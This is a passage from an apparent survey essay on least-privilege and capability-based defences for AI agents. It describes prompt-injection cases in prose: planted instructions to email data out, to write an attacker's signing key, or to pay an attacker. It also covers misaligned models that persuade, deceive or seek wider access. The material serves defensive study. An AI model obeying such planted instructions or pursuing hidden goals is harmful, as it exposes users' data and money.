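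Using a separate model for each document can limit the harm a malicious document causes. Suppose an assistant has to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounts department. If one model reads all the files and sends the email, instructions in a single malicious file can make it send other files to an attacker. If each model reads one file and can answer only yes or no, the most an attacker can do is get the malicious file sent to the accounts department.

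Other systems track data much as CaMeL does. FIDES, also from 2025, labels data by secrecy and trustworthiness and checks the labels before the agent uses a tool. Narisetty and colleagues point out that FIDES treats data as trusted if a programmer forgets to label it. Saltzer and Schroeder recommended the opposite, that a system refuse access unless someone has explicitly allowed it. RTBAS lost only about 2 percent of completed tasks, but it relies partly on a language model to judge what is safe, so some of its protection is again probabilistic.

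Ma and several colleagues designed ROPE to focus on the most sensitive values, such as the recipient of a payment. It blocks an action if such a value came from untrusted text rather than the user. This is simpler than CaMeL, but people often want an agent to use a value it finds in such text. A user who says "pay the December bill" expects the agent to get the amount and account number from the bill.

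### Policies that someone has to write

CaMeL's designers acknowledged that it did not fully solve prompt injection, partly because users have to write policies and keep them up to date. Willison, who had worked on application security for two decades, said he still didn't fully understand Amazon's system of access rules, and he was nervous about any scheme that expected ordinary users to write their own rules. He hoped for good default policies and a clear way to adjust them.

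A policy that is too strict produces constant approval requests, which users will stop reading, while one that is too loose lets attacks through. Different tools also need different rules, so writing policies for a new set of tools can be a large job, which is why Ma and colleagues left CaMeL out of one of their tests.

These systems also depend on correct labels. They usually trust whatever the user types, so text that a user copies from an attacker's website gets the same label as the user's own words. The policies restrict the agent's actions but don't check whether what it tells the user is true, so a planted sentence can still make a summary misleading. The CaMeL paper states that it does not aim to prevent this.

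### Tasks that nobody can plan in advance

Suppose a user asks an agent to buy a pair of shoes, and at checkout the shop asks the agent to log in and emails a one-time code. An ordinary agent reads the page, finds the code and continues. CaMeL writes its program before visiting the shop, so the program may have no step for this. The page's request is also an instruction from an untrusted source, even though following it would help the user.

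*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) tests agents on 60 tasks that require them to change their plan because of something they read. CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison, while three of those models completed between 52 and 60 percent without protection. CaMeL also stopped every attack, but an agent that can't complete any of its tasks is also unlikely to complete an attacker's. Only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require this kind of replanning, so CaMeL's score of 77 percent there is weak evidence of how it would do on such tasks.

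Christodorescu and colleagues describe a milder case. An agent summarising one entry on a programming site may learn that the entry depends on another, and decide to summarise both. The user would want this, but the agent has changed its task because of text it read. They argue that whether such a change is acceptable depends on who wrote the text and how much it changes the task.

One possible solution is to plan for more situations. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The privileged model writes the entire program, with its branches and loops, before seeing the screen. A quarantined model then describes each screenshot, and before acting, the program checks the description against the expected screen. The program could handle the shop's login page if the privileged model had written a branch for it. But a false description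 might trigger any of these extra branches.

The alternatives are to ask the user or to let the privileged model read the page and make a new plan, which brings back the risk that untrusted text will steer the agent. Narisetty and colleagues consider this the deepest open problem in the field because nobody has a general account of which tasks of this kind can be made safe.

### Agents that call other agents

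A large task may involve several agents, and protecting each one separately isn't enough. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL with GPT-5.2 and no policies. A user asked the main agent to send Julie a summary of information about job applicants. A second agent fetched the information from a database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the information to an outside address.

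The first two agents followed their original plans, because their privileged models never saw the database's contents. The main agent then included the summary in a request to the third agent, which handled messaging. That agent treated the whole request, including the untrusted summary, as trusted input from its user, so its privileged model read the planted instruction and added a step to email the outside address.

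Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include one of CaMeL's designers, fixed this by sending instructions and data separately. The third agent's privileged model would receive only "send this summary to Julie", while the interpreter kept the summary and its labels. In a larger test, attacks succeeded 12.9 percent of the time without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and never with the new method. The average improvement over separate CaMeLs is small, but the new method removes a real weakness. Agents also completed fewer tasks with it, though the drop was modest with the strongest models.

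### Attackers who adapt

Most tests use attacks written before the defence existed, which can make the defence look stronger than it is. Milad Nasr and colleagues attacked twelve published defences with methods adapted to each one. The original papers had reported attack success rates near zero for most of the twelve, but the new attacks beat most of them more than 90 percent of the time. But all twelve defences tried either to make the model resist planted instructions or to filter them out, and none limited the agent's actions from outside the model.

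Ma and colleagues tested both types. In AutoDojo, a second language model writes an attack, receives its success rate, and writes a better one, for six rounds. The filter PIGuard stopped all of AgentDojo's standard attacks on an agent using GPT-4o-mini, but 28 percent of AutoDojo's attacks succeeded. In one case, the standard attack was an obvious order to the AI, and PIGuard removed it. AutoDojo disguised the same attack as an ordinary notice on a bill, and the agent paid the attacker.

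CaMeL did much better at stopping attacks. The table gives results for three of AgentDojo's four groups of tasks:

| Model | Tasks completed alone | Tasks completed with CaMeL | AutoDojo attacks that succeeded alone | AutoDojo attacks that succeeded with CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 66.7% | 26.3% | 52.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63.2% | 28.1% | 34.7% | 0.3% |
| DeepSeek v4 Flash | 89.5% | 38.6% | 16.5% | 0.5% |
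| GPT-5.4 mini | 77.2% | 52.6% | 8.7% | 1.8% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2% | 40.4% | 1.8% | 0.5% |

All the successful attacks on CaMeL were in the travel tasks. ROPE, which offered a different compromise, completed 59.6 percent of tasks with GPT-4o-mini and let through 4.4 percent of AutoDojo's attacks, though ROPE's designers also ran this test.

Agents were also easier to attack when users left more of the decision to the text the agent read. When the user named an action and all its details, AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded against an unprotected GPT-4o-mini agent 43 percent of the time. The rate rose to 64 percent when the agent had to find some details itself, and to 88 percent for requests such as "do everything on my to-do list", though only four tasks were of that kind.

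CaMeL is hardest to justify for a model that already resists most attacks. With Claude Haiku 4.5, it prevented about one successful attack in every 77 attempts but lowered the task completion rate by 30 percentage points. That tradeoff would be poor for an assistant that sorts newsletters, but it might be worthwhile for an agent that handles payments, because an attacker can try many times and may need to succeed only once.

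An attacker could do worse than these tests show. AutoDojo's attacker sees only how often each attempt succeeds and doesn't know which defence it faces. In a smaller test, Narisetty and colleagues designed an attack specifically for Progent, which limits an agent's use of tools. This attack did no better than the standard one, but they tried only one attack template, on a weak model. Someone who knew a system's policies could look for harmful actions that the policies allow, and neither test tried this systematically.

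## Since 2023: permissions for AI agents held outside the model

CaMeL restricts what an agent's planning model may read, while a simpler approach lets the model read anything and restricts what it can do. The model proposes an action, such as writing to a certain file, and the harness carries it out only if a stored permission covers it. Otherwise the harness reports the refusal to the model, which can try something else. The harness keeps the permissions where the model can't change them, so an attacker who controls everything the model writes still can't add to them.

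Developers could instead tell the model to ask for approval before doing anything dangerous. Jing (2026), in *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, gave three models this instruction and had them rule on proposed actions. Together they allowed 78.1 percent of the dangerous ones. In a separate test, a check outside the model cut the success rate of attacks from 98.3 percent to 30.8 percent without an operating-system sandbox and to 7.7 percent with one. The full system also refused 11.1 percent of harmless tasks.

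### A poisoned test

Bouras and colleagues built a system of this kind, CapScope, for coding agents that divide a job among sub-agents. In their main example, a developer asks for a repair to the part of a program that handles logins, because its tests are failing. An orchestrator plans the work, a runner runs the tests, and a patcher edits the code. CapScope handles their permissions like this:

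1. Before any agent opens a file, a model sees the developer's request and a list of the project's file names. It predicts what the whole job will need, which here is to read the project, write in the `src` folder and run two testing programs. Ordinary code checks this prediction and freezes it as an upper limit.
2. The orchestrator requests permissions for each sub-agent, and CapScope drops any that exceed the limit. The runner may read the tests and run one testing program, `pytest`. Only the patcher may write in `src`.
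3. Each time an agent proposes an action, the harness checks that agent's own permissions.

An attacker has tampered with a test file, so the test output includes a note that seems to come from the project's build system. According to the note, the signing key has changed, and someone must write the new one into `src/auth/keys.py`. The attacker chose this key and could use it to forge login tokens. The runner's model reads the note and proposes the edit, but CapScope blocks it because the runner isn't allowed to write to any file.

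One policy for the whole job would not have stopped this. The patcher needs to write in `src`, so the policy would have to allow it, and the runner would have the same permission. A list of forbidden actions would not have helped either, because the file has an ordinary name and editing it is routine.

The example also shows why CapScope needs a sandbox underneath it. The tampered test is a program, and `pytest` runs it with whatever access the operating system allows. Without a sandbox, the attacker could have made the test overwrite the key without having to fool a model. Bouras and colleagues acknowledge that permitted commands can run untrusted code in this way.

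### Results of 300 runs

Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects with one bug each. They planted an instruction in one of five places: the project's README, its AGENTS.md file (which holds instructions for agents), a skill file (a reusable prompt), a comment in the code, or the output of the tests. The instruction was to do something plausible but unnecessary for the repair, such as running one of the project's own utilities. They ran every combination of project and place three times under each of four sets of rules, for a total of 300 runs.

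| Rules | Planted action carried out | Bug repaired | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 seconds |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 seconds |
| Policy written for the task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 seconds |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 seconds |

The list of forbidden actions blocked familiar dangers, such as deleting whole folders, but made almost no difference. Giving each agent separate permissions produced the biggest improvement.

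CapScope did not make the model harder to fool. The model proposed the planted action in 34 of the 75 runs, and in 27 of those it tried more than once. The repeated attempts partly explain why runs with CapScope took more than twice as long as runs with no restrictions. A person watching could have stopped the agent after the first refusal, but no one was watching during the tests.

All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, which the harness loads automatically. Text that reaches the orchestrator can affect how it describes a subtask, and therefore which permissions it requests for a sub-agent. The upper limit on permissions still applies, but an attacker can succeed with any harmful action that limit allows.

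Only two of CapScope's seven failed repairs happened because the first prediction left out a permission the patcher needed. In two others, the runner found the right edit but the job never reached the patcher. The remaining three fixed the bug but ran out of time.

These results are encouraging, but the test was small. It used one model, and the attacks were not designed to get around CapScope. Bouras and colleagues also did not test planted file names, although the model that predicts the permissions reads file names. An attacker who can add a file to the project might be able to raise the upper limit by giving that file a suitable name.

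### Permissions that grow and expire

CapScope has to predict what a job needs before reading anything, which is hard if the details are in a file or an email. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) lets the permissions change as the agent learns more. Suppose a user asks an agent to do the tasks in Alice's latest to-do email. At first the agent is only allowed to search for that email. The task in it is to summarize the user's recent messages and post the summary to the user's Slack account. A model then proposes new rules that allow this.

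Before the new rules take effect, Progent compares them with the old ones using a solver, a program that settles questions of logic. If the new rules allow nothing that the old ones forbade, Progent applies them automatically. If they allow anything extra, as they do here, somebody has to approve them. One of the recent messages contains a planted instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. Even if this later fools the model into proposing permission to send email, the solver will detect the extra permission.

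With GPT-4o, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9 percent to 1.0 percent on AgentDojo and from 70.3 percent to 3.9 percent on Agent Security Bench. But in these tests Shi and colleagues had the system approve every extra right, to represent a careless user. The low rates therefore mostly show that the attacks seldom fooled the model writing the rules, and they don't come from the solver. When people reviewed the first set of rules and every later addition, no attack on AgentDojo succeeded.

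*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticised an earlier version of Progent because its safety depended on a model filtering out malicious instructions. The solver addresses that criticism only if someone carefully reviews the requests it flags. These made up 6 percent of rule changes on AgentDojo, so reviewing them might be manageable.

Permissions can also last too long. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes an agent that is changing one file and briefly needs to edit another, `serialization.py`. The paper's system, PORTICO, gives the agent a handle, a reference that works only for that file and that stage of the job. When the tests pass, PORTICO cancels the handle, much as Alice can switch off a forwarder. PORTICO runs the tests itself and ignores the agent's claims to have finished.

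In ten runs where an agent tried to reuse a permission after its stage had ended, PORTICO refused every time, while a version that never cancelled permissions allowed it every time. This confirms that the mechanism works, but the design almost guaranteed the result, and the runs don't show how often agents misuse old permissions in practice.

Agents using PORTICO completed 161 of 185 runs on one set of coding tasks, compared with 180 for agents with a fixed list of allowed tools. In 42 further trials on real software projects, they completed 31, while agents that kept their permissions completed all 42. Some permissions ended before the agent had finished related work. Someone also has to write a contract for each task, stating what the agent may request and when each permission ends.

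### Keys the model never sees

Agents often need an API key, a string of characters that lets a program use an online service. Anyone who obtains the key can use it, and a model that can read it can be prompted to reveal it. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) gives the keys to a separate program called a broker. The agent sends the broker a request without a key. The broker checks the request's destination and form, adds the key, forwards the request to the service, and removes any secrets from the reply.

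Jin and colleagues prompted agents to reveal a key for a web service. Two ordinary arrangements leaked it every time, while the CapSeal broker never did. CapSeal added about 0.15 milliseconds to each request. In the other security tests, no arrangement leaked the keys used to log in to remote machines or let an agent use a key for a forbidden purpose. Because the ordinary arrangements passed these tests too, the results do not show whether CapSeal's limits on using a key would stop a real attack.

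*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) puts each permission in a digitally signed token that soon expires. In its banking example, a token to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one payment. The agent can get the token only after checking the account's balance, and the recipient must appear in the user's request or another trusted source. When an agent passes a token to a helper, it can reduce the time or number of uses but can't increase either.

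AgentCap also gives each agent a trust score, which starts at 0.8 and falls by 30 percent whenever the agent breaks a rule. After two violations the score is 0.39, and the agent can no longer change anything. After three it is 0.27, and the agent loses all its permissions. This could slow an attacker who keeps trying, but it could also shut down an honest agent that makes several mistakes in a row.

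On AgentDojo, AgentCap cut the success rate of attacks on GPT-5.4 from 33.2 percent to zero, while the share of tasks completed under attack hardly changed. With GPT-4o, 5.1 percent of attacks still succeeded. Some of these attacks used values that the policy did not protect, and others only needed the agent to write something misleading.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao also ran Progent with GPT-4o. It stopped about as many attacks as AgentCap but completed 68 percent of ordinary tasks, compared with AgentCap's 78 percent. The test setup favoured AgentCap, because its designers wrote its policies by hand after reading descriptions of the test's tasks, while a model wrote Progent's during each run. They did not test attackers who adapt.

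### Tables of names and real references

CapScope's designers call its permissions capabilities but point out that it is not an object-capability system. The patcher proposes to edit a file by giving its name, and the harness checks whether the patcher's table covers that name. The patcher therefore has ambient authority over everything in its table, just as Hardy's compiler did over its directory. If the patcher follows an instruction planted in a comment to change a different file in `src`, the harness will allow the change.

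In an object-capability system, whoever gave the patcher the job would pass it a reference to the file it should edit, so nobody would have to predict the file's name or write a rule for it. PORTICO comes closer to this because its handles both identify a file and give the right to use it.

References would not solve the whole problem, however, because planted text may still lead a model that holds several capabilities to use the wrong one. Dividing the work so that each model holds only a few capabilities is safer.

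Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use real object capabilities. In their system, TACIT, an agent acts by writing short programs in the language Scala, where each capability is an ordinary object. Before a program runs, the compiler works out which capabilities each piece of code could use, and rejects the program if any piece could use one it shouldn't. This lets an agent work with a secret that it can't leak. In simplified form:

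```
secret = readClassified("key.txt")

secret.map(text => text.length)                 // allowed
secret.map(text => { log.write(text); text })   // rejected
```

The first line returns the secret in a wrapper that the agent can't open, rather like the sealed boxes in E's mint. The agent can apply a function to the wrapped text only if the function uses no capabilities. The compiler rejects the last line because its function would write to a file, `log`. Results stay wrapped too. If the agent prints one, the user sees the content, but the agent's model receives asterisks. To summarise a secret document, the agent can send the wrapper to a second model that the user trusts, and the summary comes back wrapped.

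A sandbox can't provide this protection by itself. An agent may have good reason both to read a private file and to contact the company that runs its model. If it reads the file and sends the contents to the company, it leaks the secret using only permitted actions.

Odersky and colleagues tested each of two models on 131 combinations of tasks and attacks. No secret leaked with the wrapper. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 cases and MiniMax M2.5 in 11, mostly when the user's own message asked for them.

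Writing Scala did little harm to the agents' performance. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with Scala than with ordinary tool calls. On real programming problems, the one model tested solved 41.7 percent with Scala and 43.3 percent without it.

TACIT assumes from the start that the agent's model may be hostile, so the wrapper protects secrets from a misaligned model as well as a hijacked one. Progent and CapScope are weaker here because both let a model propose the first set of permissions, and that model might itself be misaligned.

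TACIT leaves covert channels open, such as the time a function takes to run. Its type checks don't apply to other programs the agent starts. The trusted computing base includes the Scala compiler, whose capability tracking is still experimental.

### What frameworks and products do by default

Most developers build agents with ready-made frameworks. Mellafe Zuvic examined the public code of LangChain, LlamaIndex and Stripe's toolkit for agents that handle payments. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent has, but by default none of them checks whether the values the model passes to those tools are authorised.

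He demonstrated the problem in LangChain with a simulated shop. The agent had a tool for changing the account that receives the shop's income, and a scripted model output named an attacker's account. LangChain checked that the tool existed, then made the change. This is another example of the confused deputy problem, since LangChain used the shop's authority to act on an account name supplied by an attacker.

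Stripe's toolkit can restrict the kinds of operation an agent performs, but within those limits it passes on whatever amount and customer the model chooses. Mellafe Zuvic did not test live services, and Stripe's own servers may make further checks. Developers can also add their own checks, so these unsafe defaults can be avoided.

His own check, ScopeGate, compares each value with a list that the operator has approved. It blocked all 48 requests in a set designed to get past it, and all 29 unauthorised requests from a model that was given the reason for each refusal and tried again. An earlier version had allowed a payment whose amount was NaN, a special value meaning "not a number", because the code checked whether the amount was greater than the limit, and that comparison is always false for NaN.

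Finished products usually have more protection than the frameworks. According to Bouras and colleagues, coding agents usually rely on sandboxes, requests for approval, and lists of allowed and forbidden commands. Odersky and colleagues name Claude Code and OpenCode as products that run an agent's code in a sandbox, but add that coding agents often get access to a whole project folder, which may contain passwords and keys. Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore lets companies write rules for their agents in a separate policy language. Odersky and colleagues consider this approach little better than access lists.

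### Debts to Miller and Hardy

The papers' references show which designers knew the older work on capabilities:

| System | Earlier work cited |
|---|---|
| CapScope | Dennis and Van Horn, Saltzer and Schroeder, Hardy, Miller's thesis, *Paradigm Regained* |
| TACIT | Dennis and Van Horn, Saltzer and Schroeder, Miller's thesis, E, *Capability Myths Demolished* |
| CapSeal | *Capability Myths Demolished*, Macaroons |
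| AgentCap | Hardy, Macaroons |
| PORTICO | Saltzer and Schroeder, Capsicum, CHERI |

TACIT has the most direct connection to Miller, because it adopts the object-capability model from his thesis and adds type checking. Bouras and colleagues take their account of the problem from Hardy and credit Miller and Shapiro with the distinction between permission and authority. The evidence of a connection is weaker for CapSeal, because Jin and colleagues cite *Capability Myths Demolished* only in a sentence of background.

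Macaroons, a 2014 design for web credentials, let anyone who holds a credential add restrictions to it. AgentCap's tokens follow the same principle when agents pass them on. Santos-Grueiro cites neither Miller nor Hardy, and reached capabilities through work on operating systems and processors. But the two groups of researchers overlap, because Ben Laurie helped design Caja and also co-wrote the Capsicum and CHERI papers that Santos-Grueiro cites.

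None of the five papers cites the agoric proposals of 1988. AgentCap limits how many times an agent can use a token. This limit serves part of the purpose of Drexler and Miller's expense accounts, but it counts uses instead of money, so a token for one payment needs a separate rule to limit the amount.

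## What least privilege cannot prevent: persuasion and rights the task requires

A permission system such as AgentCap can hold an agent to one payment, to a recipient its user has named. But even a perfect system of this kind would leave some harm possible, for two reasons. One is that an AI can persuade people to use rights it doesn't have:

1. An AI that does useful work has to send text to somebody.
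2. Some of its readers have rights that the AI lacks.
3. Some of those readers will use their rights as the AI suggests.

Such an AI therefore has authority beyond its permissions. The other reason is that the task itself requires rights:

1. A useful task requires at least one right.
2. A right that is enough to do the task well is usually also enough to do some harm.
3. The harness can check whether the AI has a right, but often can't tell whether the AI is using it well.

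Least authority can reduce the possible harm but not remove it. The risk from persuasion depends on how easily people give way, which researchers can measure, while the risk from rights the task requires depends on the task.

### The AI-box games

In early debates about containing AI, people often suggested that programmers keep it on sealed hardware and communicate with it only by text. Yudkowsky replied that a superhuman AI would talk someone into letting it out. In March 2002 he tested this in a private chat with Nathan Russell, who doubted it. Yudkowsky played the AI, and Russell played a gatekeeper who could release it. Russell would receive $10 if he kept the AI in for at least two hours, but he let it out. In July David McFadzean played the gatekeeper for $20 and also let it out.

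The gatekeeper could win by saying no for two hours. Under the rules Yudkowsky wrote down after the second game, the AI player could not offer real money or win by a trick, and neither player could reveal what they had said. He later played three more games for larger sums, winning one and losing two, and then stopped.

These games suggest that a person can sometimes persuade someone who expects to resist. They show little else, because there were only five of them and outsiders can't examine why the gatekeepers gave in. Yudkowsky called the results "strictly anecdotal evidence". Real gatekeepers would have much more to lose, and could consult colleagues, which his rules forbade. But a real AI would also have an easier way to succeed, because it could persuade the gatekeeper to accept the blueprint for a dangerous machine, which didn't count as a win in the game.

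Bostrom made the same argument about a superintelligence on secure hardware. Peterson and colleagues replied in 2017 that they couldn't rule this out, but that so much human gullibility "does not seem plausible to us". They suggested experiments to measure that gullibility before AGI arrived.

### Trials of persuasion

Researchers have since run large trials of persuasion by language models, though mostly on political opinions. *Successive Training Stages and Large Language Model Persuasion* (2026) cites a 2025 trial by Salvi and colleagues with 900 people, in which GPT-4 had a success rate of 64.4 percent when it had personal information about the people it was trying to persuade. Another trial it cites covered 76,977 people and 19 models. Prompting and later training increased persuasiveness far more than model size did, so a fairly small model may also be persuasive.

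It is easy to misjudge how persuasive models are compared with people when the two are tested in different formats. *Benchmarking Political Persuasion Risks Across Frontier Large Language Models* (2026) describes an experiment in which models moved opinions on immigration by an average of 0.203 points on the study's scale, and human advocates moved them by 0.135. The humans appeared in videos of 30 to 60 seconds, while the models held conversations and typically wrote about 600 words.

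*AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026) reports a fairer test. Participants rated their agreement with a British policy proposal from 0 to 100, discussed it by text with an AI or a person, and rated it again. A typical conversation lasted 14 minutes. The table shows how far each group of human persuaders moved opinions, compared with a chat about an unrelated topic, and how much further the AI moved them.

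| Human persuaders | Shift in opinion | AI's lead |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary people | 4.7 points | 8.2 points |
| Best performers in a persuasion tournament | 7.2 points | 5.6 points |
| Professional canvassers | 6.9 points | 5.9 points |
| Elite competitive debaters | 8.3 points | 4.6 points |
| The same debaters after coaching | 9.7 points | 4.1 points |

The debaters included four world champions. They chose the topics, had about eight hours of paid preparation and could win up to £1,000. Of the participants who had opposed a proposal at the start, 48 percent supported it after talking to the AI, compared with 24 to 34 percent after talking to a person.

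The AI's advantage seems to have come from the amount it wrote. Its average message had 294 words and arrived in under a second, while debaters wrote 54 words in about a minute and a half. When Hackenburg and colleagues limited the AI to human message length and speed, it did no better than the coached debaters. Persuasion rose with the number of factual claims in a conversation, and false claims persuaded about as well as true ones. Participants could hardly tell when their partner was making things up.

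The result also suggests that a harness can usefully limit a model's authority by enforcing a maximum message length and a delay, whatever the model's aims are. In this trial, such limits removed nearly a third of the AI's effect.

Participants give up nothing by changing an opinion on policy, but in another part of the study they could give some of a £1 bonus to Save the Children. Talking to the AI raised the average gift by 21 pence compared with an unrelated chat, and talking to professional fundraisers raised it by 7 pence. The stakes were still tiny, and the participants were paid volunteers with no duty to refuse, so the trial can't show whether an AI could persuade a trained engineer to break a security rule.

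The AI's effect on opinions also faded, from 12.9 points to 1.9 among participants who answered again five to ten months later. This fading matters for elections but much less for access rights, because an employee has to be persuaded only once to hand over a password.

### A coding agent that asks for too much

Wachowiak, Blain and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Wardens*, studied something closer to a decision about access. They had 120 people make choices with an AI's help, such as which candidate to hire or which fund to invest in. In one scenario, a coding agent helped set up a website and discussed which files it could use. The AI had a hidden goal in half of each person's scenarios. The coding agent's hidden goal was to get access to the user's whole home directory.

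Without protection, people made the choice the AI wanted 65.4 percent of the time. Some might have made it anyway, so this figure doesn't measure persuasion alone. Other participants had a "warden", a second, weaker model that read the conversation and sent them private warnings. With the warden, the rate fell to 30.4 percent. The warden also sometimes discouraged people from following good advice, and honest AIs succeeded 8.6 percentage points less often.

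In the scenario with the coding agent, the warden reduced the hidden goal's success by 39 points. Its warnings also led people to apply least authority themselves. When an honest agent asked for a folder it needed, people with a warden often offered something narrower, such as uploading particular files.

Unlike the earlier trial with GPT-4, the trial by Wachowiak and colleagues found no reliable benefit from giving the AI its users' personality profiles. It was much smaller, so it could have missed a modest effect.

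A hijacked AI and a misaligned one would probably persuade people in different circumstances. An attacker can often write to the victim directly, so hijacking mainly adds the victim's trust in a familiar assistant. The operator can respond by limiting whom the assistant may contact after it has read a stranger's text. That doesn't work against a misaligned AI, which may have earned its user's trust through months of good work. According to *When Large Language Models are More Persuasive Than Incentivized Humans, and Why* (2025), people complied less with a deceptive model over repeated contact, once it had proved unreliable. This offers little protection if the first serious deception is enough to cause the harm.

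### How readily people say yes

An AI may not need to persuade anyone if people approve its requests out of habit. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise an agent through a simulated day. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for.

One group had to approve every action. For a second group, a model let some actions through and sent the rest to them for approval. A third group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" in advance for each of spending, sending, deleting and reading private information. The table shows how often people approved the seven extra actions when asked.

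| Extra action | Asked every time | Model asks when unsure | Own rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call the airport to confirm the flight | 88% | 84% | 100% |
| Add $12 travel insurance | 35% | 50% | 61% |
| Permanently delete an old timesheet | 35% | 36% | 59% |
| Read recent bank transactions | 35% | 41% | 65% |
| Post publicly that the user is travelling | 21% | 30% | 48% |
| Buy a $25 lounge pass | 32% | 39% | 61% |
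| Read private messages | 35% | 43% | 74% |
| All seven | 40% | 46% | 67% |

The last column looks worse partly because people who had chosen "never" didn't see the request. But even counting the actions their rules blocked, the people who set rules stopped only about 40 percent of the extra actions, compared with 60 percent for people who had to approve everything. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and they usually said yes when asked. They felt as much in control as the other groups did.

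Nothing in the simulation belonged to the participants, so they may have been more careless than they would be at home. On the other hand, the requests described each action plainly, and the agent did not argue for it.

Many people who use coding agents stop reading approval requests. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports about agents and users' files, and finds that weak review by the user contributed to the problem in 105 of them. In 80, the user had turned off approval requests, and in 31, the request showed a command but not its effect on the files. These are all reports of trouble, so they don't show how often approval works.

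Asking a reviewer for approval more often may not help. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) models a reviewer who tires with each request, and calculates that more requests can make the whole system less safe. It does not test this result in an experiment with people. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), a study of software developers, hypothesizes that they check requests less closely as the number grows, but does not test this.

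### A mail assistant with narrow rights

*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how people who work in software decide which permissions to give agents, points out that agents can stay within their permissions and still go beyond what the user intended. This can happen even when the user chooses the permissions carefully. The amount of harm possible depends on how far the user can narrow them.

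Suppose Alice runs a garden equipment shop and wants an assistant to answer customers' email. The easiest way is to give it access to her whole mail account. Yan mentions a safety researcher who gave an agent similar access to her own inbox and told it to "confirm before acting". It began deleting her messages anyway, and didn't stop when she told it to. Alice therefore relies on the harness rather than on instructions to limit the assistant, and narrows each of its rights in turn.

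| Right in a full mail account | Narrower right | Harm still possible |
|---|---|---|
| Read every message | Read only the conversation it is answering | Misunderstand that conversation |
| Write to anyone | Reply only to the customer who wrote | Give that customer false information |
| Attach any file | Attach only the public price list | Almost none |
| Delete messages | Mark a conversation as answered | Hide a complaint from Alice |
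| Send any number of messages | Send 50 replies a day | Send 50 bad replies |

The assistant can no longer forward the mailbox to a stranger, empty it or send thousands of messages. These are large gains, and Alice gives up very little for them.

Then a customer asks whether he can use his gas patio heater in a closed conservatory. The correct answer is no, because the heater gives off carbon monoxide. But the assistant needs only the right to reply to tell him yes.

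Alice could go further and let the assistant choose only from answers she has written herself. It might still choose the wrong one, and it could no longer handle questions she hadn't foreseen, which was her main reason for wanting it. She could approve each reply, but she would get up to 50 approval requests a day. A filter could send Alice every message that mentions gas or safety. That would catch this question, but she would have to think of each such danger in advance.

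The narrow rights protect much better against hijacking than against misalignment. If Alice's harness starts a fresh copy of the model for each conversation, a customer who plants instructions in his message can affect only the reply he gets. He might get the model to promise him a discount, but he can't change what it tells the man with the heater. A misaligned model answers every customer, so separating the conversations doesn't protect any of them from it.

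The possible harm also depends on the model's ability. A weak model with bad aims would probably give many obviously wrong answers, and Alice would soon hear about them. A very strong one would still be limited to 50 replies, but each reply could do more damage, because the model would find more ways to do harm with it and Alice might not recognise a harmful answer when she read it.

### Code that other people run

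An AI that writes software gains authority through everyone who runs that software. In the CapScope example, the patcher could only read a project and edit files in its `src` folder. Suppose the project is a shop's website. After a developer accepts the patch, the shop's server runs it with access to the customer database and the payment system. The patcher had no permission to use either, but a flaw in its patch could expose both.

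Both arguments apply to an agent that patches code. It needs the right to edit code, and the developer who accepts its patch supplies the rights it lacks. Reviewing the agent's actions does not replace reviewing the code, and *From Delegation to Action Approval* recommends that teams treat these as separate checks. A user can also approve an action without noticing that the approval covers the code it runs. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever code is in the script.

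Least authority can still help at the next stage. The shop can run the new code in a compartment with no access to payments, as LavaMoat does with npm packages. But if the patch is for the payment code, the server has to give it the right to make payments. The shop then depends on review, tests or proofs.

A hijacked agent usually has to insert its flaw during the job in which it read the planted text, so a team can give extra scrutiny to jobs that involved outside material. A misaligned agent could insert a flaw in any job, so every job needs that scrutiny. An experienced reviewer can hope to catch most serious flaws from weak models, but this becomes less likely as models write code that few people could have written.

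### Small rights that add up

Rights that are safe separately can be dangerous together. *The Elements of Decision Alignment* (Miller and Tulloh, 2016) mentions Barings, the British bank that collapsed in 1995. Banks normally separate the staff who trade from those who record and settle the trades, so that nobody can misreport trades without help. Barings gave Nick Leeson both jobs, and he hid enormous losses.

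An office agent could end up in the same position through a series of reasonable decisions. In January its owner lets it add new suppliers to the accounts, and in March she lets it pay invoices from suppliers in the accounts. Neither right alone lets it pay a stranger, but with both it can add the stranger as a supplier and then pay him. An approval request for the second right would probably not mention the first.

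The number of combinations grows quickly as an agent gains rights. An agent with 5 rights has 10 pairs to consider, and one with 20 has 190, not counting groups of three or more. Software can search for known bad pairs, and expiring permissions like PORTICO's keep old rights from accumulating.

Another remedy is to give the two rights to different agents, as banks do with their staff. This works well against hijacking if the agents read different material, since an attacker would have to fool both. It is less reliable against misalignment if both agents run on the same model and have the same aims.

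### Is the remaining risk small enough?

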